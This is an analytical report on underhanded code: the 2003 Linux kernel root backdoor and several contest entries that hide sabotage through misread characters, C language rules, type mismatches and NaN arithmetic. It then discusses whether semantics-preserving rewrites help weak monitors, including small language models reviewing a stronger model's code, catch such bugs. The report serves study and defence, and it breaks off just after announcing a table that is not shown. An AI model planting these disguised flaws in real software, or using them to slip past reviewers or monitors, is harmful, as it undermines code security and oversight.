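# Underhanded code and semantics-preserving rewrites: can equivalent versions of a program expose a hidden bug?

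## Underhanded code, equivalent programs and weak monitors

Underhanded code is source code written to look correct while doing something harmful, and to pass for an honest mistake if somebody finds it. Most public examples come from programming contests. The best-known attempt to use it against a real system was in November 2003, when an unknown person added two lines to a copy of the Linux kernel's source code.

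### The 2003 attempt on the Linux kernel

Linux developers at the time kept the master copy of their code in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them disliked it, so BitMover, the company behind BitKeeper, also maintained a clone in another system, CVS. On 5 November Larry McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, told the kernel mailing list that somebody had modified the clone directly. A reader asked what had changed, and McVoy (2003), in *Re: BK2CVS problem*, posted the added lines:

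```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines are in a function called `wait4`, which a program calls to wait for another process. `options` holds the caller's flags, and `current->uid` is the user ID of the running program. User ID 0 is "root", the account that may do anything on the machine. To someone reading at normal speed, the lines look like an argument check that returns the error code for an invalid argument if the caller passes this odd pair of flags and is root.

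But in C, two equals signs compare and one assigns. When a program calls `wait4` with exactly that pair of flags, the left half of the condition is true, so the machine evaluates the right half, which sets the user ID to 0 and makes the caller root. An assignment in C evaluates to the value stored, here 0, which C treats as false. The whole condition therefore fails, and the line that would have set the error code never runs. A program that passes any other flags never reaches the assignment, so ordinary use and testing don't reveal the bug.

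An expert reading casually would take all this for innocuous error checking, according to Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013). The reader expects a comparison and so reads the single `=` as `==`. Tomas Szepe (2003), replying in the same thread, pointed out that the extra parentheses around the assignment also avoid a warning from gcc, the standard compiler. C's grammar requires those parentheses for an assignment here, but many programmers put them around comparisons out of habit, so they don't look suspicious.

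The mailing list has the best evidence of how well the disguise worked. McVoy knew that the two lines were unauthorised and had just pasted them into an email, but he did not see their effect. One reader replied that they looked odd, another explained what they did about twenty minutes after the post, and McVoy answered, "Good eyes, I missed that."

The backdoor was less successful as deniable code. Wheeler (2020), in *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code*, a study for the Institute for Defense Analyses, calls the trick a one-character difference, which is true if the line is compared with the honest check it imitates. But the change added two new lines to the kernel, and they make little sense even with the missing character restored. The next line of the function overwrites the error code. `wait4` also has no reason to use the user ID, which InfoQ's *A Look Back at the Linux Kernel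 Backdoor* (2013) takes as proof of intent.

A nightly BitMover job, not a human reader, caught the change by comparing checksums of the public CVS copy with BitMover's own. The edit was logged under the name of a known developer, who denied making it, and the entry lacked the pointer to an approved change that every genuine entry carried. Who made the edit remains unknown. McVoy had the file repaired within a day. He thought that without the check, a CVS user might have sent the lines back to the main kernel inside an innocent patch. The maintainer who took in patches for releases disagreed, writing in *Re: BK2CVS problem* (2003) that core files were read through and that the people who merged code did not use the CVS copy. Debian's vulnerability record, *CVE-2003-1161*, lists the backdoor as never released.

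### Bugs, backdoors and obfuscation

A backdoor differs from an honest bug in that someone plants it deliberately, to make a program misbehave under conditions they can bring about. The input or circumstance that sets it off is the trigger, which in the kernel case was the pair of flags. Thomas and Francillon complained in *Backdoors* that the word had no rigorous definition in either research or the press. The doctoral thesis *Backdoor detection systems for embedded devices* (Thomas, 2018) defines it by the same two elements, because the system must *intentionally* include a *means to trigger* functionality that subverts its expected security.

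Intent is hard to judge because it is not in the code. A reviewer can establish that a line is dangerous without ever learning whether someone meant it to be. In February 2014, Apple patched a flaw in the code that secures connections on its phones. A duplicated line, `goto fail;`, had no condition attached, so the procedure always ended early. *Was the iOS SSL Flaw Deliberate?* (Schneier, 2014) repeats three marks of a good backdoor that the security writer Bruce Schneier had listed earlier: a low chance of discovery, high deniability if discovered, and few conspirators. The Apple flaw had all three, but it was also a mistake that anyone could make when pasting code.

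Underhanded code exploits this gap. It has to go unnoticed when someone reads it, and preferably even when they understand it. A backdoor does not have to be hard to recognise. For example, a reader who comes to a password written into the program will usually know that it is a backdoor.

Unlike underhanded code, obfuscated code is openly hard to read. The long-running International Obfuscated C Code Contest (IOCCC) asks for the most obscure program possible within its rules, partly as an ironic lesson in the value of good style. Hackaday's *The Winners of the 2025 Obfuscated C Code Contest* (2026) covered the latest round. Wheeler leaves obfuscated code out of his study because a reviewer who cannot follow a program can report that and refuse to trust it for that reason alone, a reason reviewers don't have with underhanded code.

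### The contests and what they reward

The earliest underhanded contest that Wheeler found was Daniel Horn's misleadingly named *Obfuscated Vote Counting Contest* (Horn, 2004). In October 2004, Horn invited programmers to write C code that appears correct but miscounts votes, and added that obviously incorrect code was not welcome. *The Obfuscated V contest* describes the judging procedure. On 2 November, the day of the American presidential election, judges inspected the entries by eye, picked the one that looked most correct, and then ran it. If it miscounted in favour of a candidate, it won. If it counted properly, they moved to the next most convincing entry. In one of the two categories, programs had to count correctly on 1 November and miscount the day after.

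Scott Craver, a professor of information security at Binghamton University, started the Underhanded C Contest in 2005. In the contest's *FAQ* he recalls being impressed that a short program that merely counts characters could fail on one specific day, so that testing would miss the fault. The contest ran until 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015. Each year it set a small data-processing task and a way for the code to secretly subvert it. In the last round, for a $1,000 prize from the non-profit Nuclear Threat Initiative, entrants wrote the part of a warhead inspection system that compares a radiation measurement with a reference. The code had to return "yes" for a fake warhead, but only under conditions that the cheating country could arrange.

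Other communities copied the format. In September 2014, Adam Caudill and Taylor Hornby launched a version for cryptography (Caudill, 2015, *On the Underhanded Crypto Contest*), which ran until 2018. Its rules, reposted to a mailing list by ianG (2014) in *Underhanded Crypto*, suggested entries such as a chat protocol that looks secure to every expert but that anyone who knows one fixed key can read. In a 2015 JavaScript contest, entrants had to leak a generated key to a remote server; 34 of the 40 entries were valid. One entrant, Jonathan Mann, used = in place of ==, as the kernel attacker had, because the error is common enough to pass as an honest mistake (Mann, 2015, *Spotting Malicious Code Hidden in Plain Sight*). The organisers' page for the Underhanded Solidity Contest (2022) lists contests in 2017, 2020 and 2022 for Solidity, a language for programs that hold and move money on a blockchain.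 A Rust contest announced in December 2016 never published any entries.

The scoring rules hardly vary, and three of them, all found in the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2015 Challenge* (2015), matter for what follows.

Short, readable entries score higher because a reviewer who misses the fault has still looked at every line and accepted it. In a long, tangled program, the reviewer may miss a fault through fatigue, which is little evidence that it was well hidden. Craver gave a seventy-two-line entry extra credit for being short and readable in the round he judged in 2013.

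A bug also scores higher if the programmer can plausibly deny having intended it once it is found. The 2014 task was to leak the existence of secret government surveillance. In *The 7th Underhanded C Contest is now Open*, Craver (2014) called deniability particularly crucial for this task, because a programmer caught leaking on purpose would be in serious trouble. The scoring rule pushes entrants towards mistakes that honest programmers make, which a reviewer cannot treat as suspicious by their form alone.

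The third rule rewards errors that still look innocent under syntax colouring, the code-editor feature that shows comments, numbers and keywords in different colours. Colouring changes only how the program looks. It exposes some tricks, such as live code disguised as a comment, but not others, such as a single = in the right place.

Craver treats errors of perception, such as mistaking the letter l for the digit 1, as equal to deep faults in how C handles memory, because the code only has to get past the reader. The 2017 Solidity rules, which Felix Stalder reposted, also allow misleading names.

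Contest results are imperfect evidence about ordinary code review. The judges know that every entry is malicious, which an ordinary reviewer does not, so an entry that gets past them has passed a stricter test. But the contests mostly publicise their winners, so outsiders can't easily tell how often the tricks failed. Wheeler asked for the complete set of Underhanded C entries and had not received it when he wrote.

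### Equivalent programs

Two programs P and Q are equivalent, written P ≡ Q, if P(x) = Q(x) for every input x, where P(x) covers everything the program does with x, including whether it ever stops. The set of all programs equivalent to P is its equivalence class. A semantics-preserving rewrite changes a program's text but keeps the program in the same equivalence class. Examples include renaming a variable consistently and changing the indentation in C.

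Take `uid` to be an ordinary integer variable and `deny()` a function that refuses access. Each of these three lines is then a complete program fragment, and all three are equivalent:

```c
if (uid = 0) deny();
uid = 0; if (uid != 0) deny();
uid = 0;
```

The first line has the same form as the kernel trick. The second moves the assignment out of the condition and tests the result. Since `uid` is now 0, the test can never succeed, so the third drops it. A reader who skims past the first line will very probably stop at the third, which openly grants root access. Correcting the first line to `if (uid == 0) deny();` would not count as an equivalent rewrite, because it changes what the program does, even if it matches what the author seems to have meant.

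So a rewrite never removes a backdoor, because every program in the class has the same trigger and does the same harm. But a rewrite can remove the disguise, as in the third line, which is as dangerous as the first but no longer underhanded.

Whether two programs are equivalent depends on what counts as behaviour. Wheeler lists a small contest for sorting programs that run much more slowly on a competitor's platform. An ordinary sorter and a sabotaged one produce the same output for every input, so they are equivalent unless the definition includes running time. The C standard also leaves the effect of some operations undefined, and two compilers may treat them differently. A claim that two C programs are equivalent may therefore hold only for a given compiler and its settings.

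No general procedure can decide whether two programs are equivalent. For any program M, let A be a program that returns 0 for every number n, and let B be a program that runs M for n steps, then returns 1 if M has stopped by then and 0 if it has not. A and B are equivalent exactly when M never stops, so a procedure that decided equivalence would also decide whether any given program stops, which Alan Turing proved impossible in 1936. If M stops only after a billion steps, tests on smaller inputs will find no difference between A and B, much as tests that lack the trigger will find no difference between a backdoored program and a clean one.

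Undecidability rules out a universal test for equivalence, but it can still be possible to prove whether two particular programs are equivalent. One can also produce equivalent versions of a program P by applying only rewrites already known to be safe. The neighbourhood of P is the set of versions that a chosen set of rewrites can reach. (In machine learning, the word covers any examples counted as close to a given one.) This neighbourhood is only a small part of the equivalence class, and which part depends on the rewrites. A tool that can only rename variables cannot turn the first line of the example into the third.

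### The weak monitor

A weak monitor is a person or model that judges whether code is safe but is less capable than the code's author, or than a model trained on the monitor's verdicts. Examples include a hurried maintainer reading a patch from a cleverer attacker and a small language model checking the output of a larger one.

Suppose such a monitor classifies a backdoored program P as safe. Someone then rewrites P as an equivalent program Q, and the monitor, given Q without P or its earlier verdict, classifies Q as unsafe. Because the two programs behave alike, one of the verdicts must be wrong, and we can tell this without knowing whether P is safe. If the alarm on Q is correct, it applies to P as well, so the second verdict corrects the first. On the kernel mailing list, the correction came from a second reader of the same code. The hope is that giving the same reader a second version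 of the code could also expose the error, which would be valuable when no better reader is available and a machine can generate hundreds of rewrites.

One can pool the verdicts, for instance by a vote, or use them as pseudolabels to train a stronger model. Pseudolabels are labels from a fallible teacher, used as training data in place of true labels. Training also requires the stronger model, the student, to give equivalent programs the same answer. The student may then make fewer errors than its teacher, an effect called pseudolabel correction. This depends, among other things, on expansion, which roughly means that the programs the teacher misjudges have enough correctly judged programs as neighbours.

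Neither method is sure to work. A disagreement shows that the monitor was wrong about some version, but not which one, and the alarm on Q may be a false one set off by clumsy rewritten code. The monitor may also be wrong about every version, and then there is no disagreement to notice. Renaming every variable in the two kernel lines, for example, leaves the single = as easy to miss as before. Whoever writes underhanded code may also know which rewrites the reviewers use, and can pick a fault that stays hard to spot after them.

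## How underhanded programs mislead their readers

A reader who approves an underhanded program usually thinks they understand it but is mistaken. Wheeler (2021), in a post to a security mailing list, described such code as "easy to understand WRONGLY". Each trick therefore depends on a false belief, which may be about the characters on the screen, a rule of the language, the contents of another file, how computers handle numbers, or whether the method does the job at all.

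In his 2020 study, Wheeler recommended sorting all known samples of underhanded code by the weakness they exploit, though he had not fully done so himself. Sorting them by the false belief that misleads the reader is more useful here, because an equivalent version of a program helps a reader only if it makes them doubt that belief.

Many of the best-documented tricks come from the 2015 Underhanded C Contest, which was about warhead inspection. *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, 2016) describes the winner and runners-up from more than 40 entries. Entrants wrote a function called `match`, which compares two gamma-ray spectra. Each spectrum is a list of gamma-ray counts, one for each narrow band of energy, called a bin. Plutonium produces peaks in particular bins. `match` returns 1 if the spectrum of the warhead under test is close enough to a trusted reference, as determined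 by a threshold, and 0 otherwise. Apart from its planted fault, the function had to reject fakes reliably.

### Misread characters and layout

Josh Lospinoso's entry is one letter short. It looks for spectra with values too large for the computer to represent, which C stores as infinity, and handles them with this line:

```c
return isinf(testLength)&&sinf(referenceLength) ? MATCH : NO_MATCH;
```

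`isinf` tests whether a number is infinite, so a reader will probably take the line to mean that two infinite spectra match. But the second call is missing its first letter, which makes it `sinf`, a standard function that computes a sine. C treats every number except zero as true, and a sine is almost never exactly zero, so the line almost always returns a match when the test spectrum is infinite, whatever the reference is.

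The Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* asked for a program that looks up luggage records at an airport and loses some of them. Sam Blackburn's winning entry censors swear words using a list of words and replacements, but the list is missing a comma. C joins two neighbouring strings into one if no comma separates them, so "damn" gets a nine-character replacement instead of "d*mn". The longer text runs past the end of the comment field and overwrites the flag that marks a record for deletion, so the record disappears when a check-in clerk types "damn".

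A runner-up that year, RHays, hid a wrong character among similar ones. C ends each string with a special character, written `'\0'`. One long condition in the program tests for it correctly, but a few terms later tests for the digit `'0'` instead. Some terms in the condition are unnecessary, and according to the contest's review, they set up a pattern that fools the eye and make the bug look like a beginner's mistake.

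Gregory Stewart's 2015 entry sets up a pattern in the layout. Several of its functions end with the same lines: `goto done;`, then an `error:` label that sets the result to 0, then a `done:` label that returns the result. In the function that supplies storage for one pair of readings, the ending looks like this:

```c
        *s = p;
        goto done;
    }

error:
    result = 0;

done:
    return result;
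```

The `goto done;` is inside the closing brace, so it belongs only to the branch that reuses old storage. The branch that creates new storage falls through to `error:` and reports failure, even though it has supplied a valid block filled with zeros. The calling function receives the failure code and doesn't copy the readings in, so the test value, reference value and threshold in that block all stay at zero. A difference of zero does not exceed a threshold of zero, so the bin counts as a match.

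The program starts with a pool of reusable blocks, but another bug returns only one block to the pool after each test. Once the pool runs out, only the first bin affects the answer, because all the others match automatically. Craver called the bug perceptual, but he also found it suspicious that the program copied an array into a linked structure when a simple loop would have done the comparison.

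Readers can still misread a program when they know it contains a trick. The organiser of the 2004 vote-counting contest attributed the fault in Ryan Cumings's program to a swap of the letter O and the digit 0. Wheeler confirmed the swap but found that the program miscounted the votes because it misused the remainder operator elsewhere.

### Misapplied rules of the language

Michael Dunphy's 2015 entry contains a safety check that cannot work. Its helper function `dot` multiplies two spectra bin by bin and adds up the products. If the total is zero, infinite or undefined, `dot` sets `err = 1`, and `match` later rejects the warhead if `err` is greater than 0. The two lines that matter are far apart in purpose but close together on the page:

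```c
static inline double dot(double *x, double *y, int n, unsigned int err)

if ( err > 0 ) return 0; // test fails for any invalid data
```

C gives a function copies of its arguments, so `dot` sets only its own copy of `err`, and the `err` in `match` stays at 0. To change that `err`, Dunphy would have needed to pass its address or, in C++, which the contest also accepted, add an `&` to the declaration. Craver notes that experienced C programmers look for a check before every division. Some entrants therefore supplied one that does nothing. A reader who finds the check has less reason to work out what an invalid value would do.

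In the 2008 contest, entrants wrote a program that blacks out rectangles in an image while leaving the hidden part recoverable. Linus Åkesson took third place with a macro, a piece of text that the compiler substitutes into the program before translating it:

```c
#define BYTESPERPIXEL(fits8bits) (3 << (!fits8bits))
```

An ordinary colour image needs three bytes per pixel and a finer-grained one needs six. The macro starts from 3 and is supposed to double it if the colours do not fit in eight bits. The program uses `BYTESPERPIXEL(256 > max)` when it reads the image and `BYTESPERPIXEL(max < 256)` when it writes the result. In ordinary arithmetic the two conditions are the same. But after substitution the `!`, which means "not", applies only to the first term:

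```c
3 << (!256 > max)   /* !256 is 0; 0 > max is false; result 3 */
3 << (!max < 256)   /* !max is 0 or 1, always below 256; result 6 */
```

The program therefore reads three bytes per pixel and writes six. The original image comes directly after the blacked-out copy in memory, so writing twice the proper length appends the original to the output file, where image viewers ignore it. Parentheses around `fits8bits` in the macro's body would have prevented this.

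Craver (2009), in *2008 Winners*, draws a general principle from the entry: make the common case evil and the uncommon case wrong. Almost all images in this format use eight-bit colour, and all of those leak. The rare images with finer-grained colour make the program fail completely, but few people will try one. The macro seems to be there to support these rare images, and anyone who does try one finds an ordinary bug.

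The contestants exploit misunderstandings that programmers already have. An "atom of confusion" is a small code pattern that makes programmers predict the wrong behaviour and that has a clearer equivalent. *Does Confusing Code Confuse LLMs?* (van de Wetering, Solovyeva and Castor, 2026) reports that some atoms raised error rates by as much as 60% in the original experiments with programmers, by Gopstein and colleagues. These atoms include operator precedence, which Åkesson's macro exploits, and assignments used as values, as in the kernel backdoor. *Atoms of Confusion in Java* (Langhout and Aniche, 2021) tested 14 patterns and found participants 2.7 to 56 times more likely to make mistakes with seven of them.

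Atoms of confusion, which are small code patterns that readers easily misread, are also common in honest code. A survey of 14 large C and C++ projects, including the Linux kernel, found one every 23 lines on average, so a reviewer can't treat them as a sign of malice. But when Langhout and Aniche showed participants code with an atom and an equivalent version without it, they rated the version with the atom as more confusing for 10 of the 14 patterns. An underhanded programmer has to avoid making readers feel confused, because a confused reader slows down.

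Language models seem to share some of these weaknesses. *How do Humans and LLMs Process Confusing Code?* (Abdelsalam, Peitek and colleagues, 2025) found that Qwen2.5-Coder-32B assigned unusually low probabilities to confusing passages, and that these correlated with signs of confusion in programmers' brain recordings. The probabilities measure how unexpected the code is to the model, not whether the model gets it wrong. When van de Wetering and colleagues asked three more recent models to predict what programs would output, confusing operator precedence did not visibly reduce their accuracy. ChatGPT's score fell from five out of five to two when the programs used octal (base 8) numbers, but with only five programs per pattern, each error changes the score by 20 percentage points.

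Karen Pease's winning entry in the 2014 Underhanded C Contest, where the task was to leak the existence of secret surveillance, depends on a macro that looks like a function. The macro, `__isleap(year)`, is a standard test for leap years. A function would evaluate its argument once, but this macro copies the argument's text into up to three places, and in Pease's program that text also writes an entry to an audit record. The extra entries overrun the space set aside for them, and a later write sets the user's account creation date to zero. The contest's *Review of the 2014 Challenge* describes several more mistakes that the chain requires, all in code that appears to be there to prove compliance.

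A rule from another language can also mislead readers. Wheeler describes a Python program that relies on `//`, which starts a comment in many languages but not in Python. The trick works only on people who know one of those languages, as most professional programmers do.

### Facts in separate files

Åkesson won the 2015 contest with 66 lines of code in three files. Åkesson (2016), in *Faking Fissile Material*, published the entry together with its official documentation and a separate explanation of the trick. These are the lines that matter, without the rest:

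```c
/* match.h */
typedef double float_t;
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length);

/* match.c */
#include "match.h"

/* spectral_contrast.c */
#include <math.h>
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length) { /* ... */ }
```

The `typedef` line makes `float_t` another name for `double`, an eight-byte number. `match.c` includes that definition, but `spectral_contrast.c`, which does the comparison, does not. The compiler doesn't report `float_t` as undefined there because `math.h`, included for its square-root function, defines a standard type of the same name. On most current machines that type is a four-byte `float`.

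The compiler translates each C file separately, so it never processes the two definitions together. If either file included both headers, compilation would stop with an error. Instead, `match.c` passes an array of eight-byte numbers to a function that reads four-byte numbers.

The function therefore covers only half the spectrum. For a spectrum of 1,000 bins, it reads 1,000 four-byte numbers, which span the same memory as the first 500 eight-byte ones. Peaks in the right half don't affect this comparison.

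The heights of the remaining peaks also change. Both formats store a number as a sign, an exponent e and a fraction f, representing ±(1 + f) × 2^e. A `double` has 11 bits for the exponent and 52 for the fraction, while a `float` has 8 and 23. The counts in a spectrum are whole numbers, and Åkesson assumed that they stay below about a million. Such a number fills only the left end of the fraction, so the right half of the `double` is all zeros and equals 0 when read as a `float`. These extra zeros are at the same positions in both spectra and don't affect the comparison.

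The left half contains the sign, the whole exponent and the first 20 bits of the fraction. The `float` format has room for only the first 8 of the 11 exponent bits, so the last three become part of the fraction. Removing the last three binary digits of the exponent divides it by eight, which roughly takes the eighth root of the number.

The exact result follows from the two formats. A `double` stores its exponent as E = e + 1023. If q is the quotient and r the remainder when E is divided by 8, then a positive number v = (1 + f) × 2^e turns into:

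squash(v) = 2^(q − 127) × (1 + (r + f)/8)

The number 10 is 1.25 × 2^3, which gives E = 1026, q = 128 and r = 2, so it becomes 2 × (1 + 2.25/8), or about 2.56. The number 1,000 is about 1.953 × 2^9, which gives E = 1032, q = 129 and r = 0, so it becomes about 4.48, and a peak 100 times as high as another ends up only about 1.75 times as high.

The program prepares the spectra before comparing them. It averages over 16 neighbouring bins, takes the difference between each bin and the next, and averages again. The honest purpose of these steps is to remove noise and the slope of the background. But dividing by 16, a power of two, also leaves the fraction bits unchanged, and most terms cancel when the differences are averaged, so the right half of each `double` stays empty. The differences can be positive or negative, and squashing leaves little except their sign. The comparison therefore depends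 on where the peaks in the left half are, and hardly at all on how high they are.

A cheating country can therefore use a small amount of real fissile material, which puts peaks in the correct places. The program separately checks that the total radiation is high enough, so the country adds another isotope with strong peaks in the right half of the spectrum. These peaks raise the total, but the comparison ignores them.

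Åkesson's documentation describes a test that makes the detector seem reliable. He generated 1,000 artificial materials, simulated two measurements of each, and searched for the highest threshold at which `match` would accept the pair. He did the same for 1,000 pairs of different materials, and used both sets of results to recommend a threshold of 0.6. These tests ran the faulty code but did not expose the fault, because randomly chosen materials usually have peaks in different places, a difference the faulty comparison can still detect.

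Åkesson's private explanation describes a second test, in which he made a forgery for each of 1,000 artificial materials by mixing 10% of the real material with 90% of a random one that had a strong peak on the right. A large proportion of these crude forgeries failed to fool the detector. He did not think this would be a problem for a cheating country, which could try many mixtures and pick the best, or design one by hand. One of his examples passed at thresholds up to 0.72, above the recommended 0.6.

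The judges gave seven reasons for their choice. A country could use the fault without touching the computer, and the program compared spectra by a method that people use in practice. A reader who missed the type mismatch would find nothing else suspicious in the sixty-odd lines. The judges also admired how the mismatch produces usable results and exploits the fact that counts are whole numbers, a property that the preparation steps preserve. The Nuclear Threat Initiative's *"Underhanded C" Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies* adds that arms control had no standards for writing or reviewing code.

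The documentation also misleads readers. In it, the author warns that a country might present only a small fraction of the expected fissile material and gives this as the reason for checking total radiation. To a reader who had thought of this fraud, the author would appear to have dealt with it.

Alex Olson won in 2013 with a similar mismatch between files. In the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2013 Challenge*, entrants had to write a function that measures how many friendship links separate two users of a social network, where closer users get more access. One of Olson's files declares that a validation function stores its answer in an `int`, but the file containing the function uses a `long`, which is twice as large on his target machines. The extra bytes overwrite the next variable in memory, which holds the distance. This is harmless for most users, but for a user called `!!!` the answer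 is negative, and the extra bytes set the distance to the closest possible value. An attacker with that name gets full access to everyone's account, even with no friends on the network.

The 2007 winner, Emmanuel Colbus, used a declaration that conflicts with a standard library instead of with another of his own files. His encryption program declares that `time()`, which returns the current time, takes no argument, but the real function takes an address at which to store the time. When the program calls it without an address, the function uses whatever value is in memory where the address should be, and overwrites a debugging flag. About once in 256 runs, this turns debugging on, and the program writes the encryption key into the encrypted file. The Underhanded C Contest described the two calls to `time()` as probably the most innocent-looking part of the code.

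### Numbers that break the rules of arithmetic

About a third of the 2015 entries used NaN, short for "not a number". C produces this value for undefined calculations such as 0/0 or the square root of −1. Most calculations that involve a NaN also give NaN. But a comparison such as `x < 5` has to come out true or false, and with a NaN it comes out false. Compare these two lines, of which Peter Eastman's entry contains the first:

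```c
return (correlation < threshold ? 0 : 1);
return (correlation >= threshold ? 1 : 0);
```

The two versions return the same answer for every ordinary number, but for a NaN the first returns 1 and the second returns 0. A reader who believes that a number is either below a threshold or not below it will see no difference, and that belief is correct for numbers in the mathematical sense.

Eastman's program subtracts the expected background radiation from each bin and replaces negative results with zero. If a fake never exceeds the background, every bin becomes zero, the correlation becomes 0/0, and the fake passes. Dunphy's program, as Craver printed it, ends with the second form. Under standard arithmetic, a NaN there would make the program report no match, so the broken error check is not enough on its own to produce a false match.

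The judges shortlisted few NaN entries. Some relied on the cheating country putting a NaN in the input, some divided without any check, and others needed contrived conditions. They liked Philipp Klenze's entry, which compares the spectra by calculating how probable each count is. The numbers in that formula grow so quickly that a bin with a count of about 1,700 or more produces a NaN. Such bugs usually require unrealistically large inputs, but a radioactive source inside the fake could plausibly reach this count.

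Stephen Dolan's entry exploits rounding. It adds up the squared differences between the two spectra and then subtracts the largest, supposedly to ignore a single outlier. A reader will assume this leaves the sum of the others, but a `double` is accurate to only about 16 decimal digits. If the first difference is 100,000,000, its square is 10^16, and adding 1 to that gives 10^16 again. Every later difference of 1 disappears in the same way, so subtracting the outlier leaves exactly zero, a perfect match. The large difference has to come first, because small squares already added together may have a sum too large to be rounded away.

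Whole numbers have limits too. In a 2013 entry, Gaëtan Leurent turned a user's name into a position in a table and used `abs`, the absolute value, to keep it from being negative. The usual 32-bit integers run from −2,147,483,648 to 2,147,483,647, so the lowest number has no positive counterpart, and in practice `abs` often returns it unchanged. Leurent then added an explicit check for negative positions, which should have caught this. But the C standard doesn't define the result of `abs` for this number, so the compiler may assume that this case never occurs and remove the check as redundant. Without the check, the name of a specially created account leads to position −2, outside the table, where the program overwrites the distance between two users.

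### A wrong method, correctly programmed

John Meacham won the 2008 contest with a program that a reader can understand line by line and still approve. It blacks out part of an image stored as text, where decimal numbers give the brightness of each pixel's red, green and blue. Zero means black. Inside the chosen rectangle, the 55-line program replaces every digit with `0` and copies everything else:

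```c
putchar('0');
```

A value of 255 therefore becomes 000, and a value of 7 becomes 0. Both appear black on the screen, but the file still shows how many digits each number had. In a scanned document, white paper gives three-digit numbers and black ink can give single digits, so anyone who opens the file as text may be able to recover the hidden words. The Underhanded C Contest counted even a faint trace as a leak, since an attacker may only need to tell which of two words is under the block. Stronger leaks earned more points.

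A reader can mistake blacking out pixels for deleting the information in them. Meacham's program turns every selected pixel black, but the task was to make the original unrecoverable. Craver noted that the program zeroes the pixels without changing the size of the file, unlike entries that appended the original to the end. The unchanged size makes the program look cleaner, but it results from keeping the original digit counts, which leak information about the blacked-out pixels.

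The method is also easy to excuse. Meacham commented under the results that he had to process the file one character at a time to get around a problem with `fgets`, a standard function for reading text. He wrote that a version without the leak would have been more complicated or buggy.

The flaw in Domenico Andreoli's 2014 entry is an action that the code performs openly. When a message matches a surveillance request, the program saves it along with the user's profile picture, which it downloads from an address the user chose. A user who watches that address can see the download and learn of the surveillance. Craver wrote in his review that he stared at the short, readable program for some time without finding the bug, which was in an action mentioned only in a comment at the top.

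### Triggers in the data and in the environment

The 2015 judges looked at what triggers a fault as well as the belief that hides it. They called a fault data-triggered if an unusual spectrum activates it, as with Åkesson's mixture of isotopes or Klenze's strong peak, and environment-triggered if the cause lies in the computer running the program. Sarah Newman and S. Gilles, for example, submitted programs that misbehave when someone changes the number of available processors during the calculation.

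Stephen Oman's entry divides the radiation counts by the length of the scan and checks only that this length is not zero. If someone sets the clock back during the scan, the length becomes negative, and so do all the divided counts. The comparison tests only whether certain ratios are small enough, so negative ratios always pass.

Ghislain Lemaur used a log file as the trigger. If the program cannot open the file, it writes a message containing the user ID of the file's owner. A five-digit ID makes the message two bytes too long for its buffer, and the extra bytes slightly change the exponent 2.0 that the program uses to square differences. The log still shows the exponent as 2.0, but it is no longer a whole number, so raising a negative difference to that power gives NaN, which lets the fake pass.

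The judges generally preferred data-triggered faults because these need no further assumptions about what the cheating country can do, but they did not dismiss the others. Inspection experts told them that physical custody of the machines would not completely rule out tampering, and Craver added that a change may be too subtle for anyone to think of forbidding it. Data triggers can also be unrealistic. Lospinoso's and Dolan's programs both need implausibly large readings. Stewart's needs a series of tests to use up the pool and then a spectrum whose first bin is close to the reference, so it does not fit clearly into either category.

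Environment triggers also affect what it means for two programs to be equivalent. If the input x in P(x) contains only the two spectra and the threshold, tests cannot vary the clock or a file's owner. Two versions of `match` could then agree on every such input, even though only one of them accepts a fake after someone sets the clock back. To be equivalent for security purposes, they must also agree in every machine state an attacker can cause.

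## What each kind of rewrite does to a hidden bug

A rewrite that preserves a program's behaviour also preserves any bug in it, but the new text may change how likely a reader is to notice the bug.

Researchers who test vulnerability detectors sometimes use a weaker definition of "semantics-preserving". In *Uncovering the Limits of Machine Learning for Automatic Vulnerability Detection*, Risse and Böhme (2023) imagine an oracle g that labels code 1 if it has a security flaw and 0 if it doesn't. They call a rewrite t semantics-preserving on a set of programs if g(t(c)) = g(c) for every program c in the set, and label-inverting if it changes the label. A rewrite that swaps one flaw for another would count as semantics-preserving, although it changes the program's behaviour. An unchanged label would be enough for pooling a monitor's verdicts, but nobody has the oracle, so in practice the way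 to be sure the label is unchanged is to preserve the behaviour.

### Three outcomes

A rewrite can leave the bug in place and still hidden, or leave it in place but visible. If the bug disappears, the rewrite was not equivalent. The last line of Peter Eastman's 2015 warhead detector can illustrate all three outcomes. If the correlation is NaN, the value C gives to undefined calculations, the published line accepts the warhead:

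```c
/* published */
return (correlation < threshold ? 0 : 1);

/* bug still hidden */
if (correlation < threshold) return 0;
return 1;

/* bug visible */
if (isnan(correlation)) return 1;
return correlation >= threshold;

/* bug gone */
return correlation >= threshold;
```

The first three versions are equivalent as long as the threshold is an ordinary number. The third explicitly accepts a warhead when the program could not calculate its correlation, and few reviewers would approve that. However, a person who thinks of writing `isnan` there has probably already found the bug. A tool could add this check to every floating-point comparison without knowing which one matters, but the code would be much longer.

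A rewrite that is not equivalent can also create a bug. Michael Dunphy's entry ends with `r >= threshold ? 1 : 0`, which rejects a NaN. If someone rewrites this as `r < threshold ? 0 : 1`, a scan with no counts in any bin produces 0/0, which is NaN, and passes as a warhead because Dunphy's check for invalid data does nothing. Rewriting on the mistaken assumption that a number is always either below a threshold or at or above it therefore repairs Eastman's program but completes the attack in Dunphy's.

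### Seven families of rewrites

In *Semantic Robustness of Models of Source Code*, Ramakrishnan, Henkel and colleagues (2020) treat a rewrite as a function that takes a program and, where necessary, a parameter such as a new variable name. They apply rewrites in sequence, so T rewrites give T^k sequences of length k, before counting the choice of parameters. Their Java suite has eight rewrites, which would give 32,768 sequences of length five.

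But a large number of versions may contain little variety. Three of the eight rewrites rename things, and three more add unused code, a print statement or an error handler. The other two unroll loops and replace the constants "true" and "false" with equivalent expressions. None of these would expose any of the six bugs in the table below, however often a tool applied them. Whether they preserve semantics also depends on what counts as behaviour. The 2008 contest programs write the finished image to standard output, so an added print statement could corrupt the image.

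The table covers a wider range of rewrites. It is this report's own analysis, done by working through the published code by hand, and not a result from the works cited. "Hidden" and "visible" both mean that the bug is still there. "Visible" means that the new text contradicts the false belief the trick depends on, so a competent reader of that passage should notice. This is a judgement about the text that no experiment has tested. "Gone" means that the natural way to carry out the rewrite removes the harmful behaviour.

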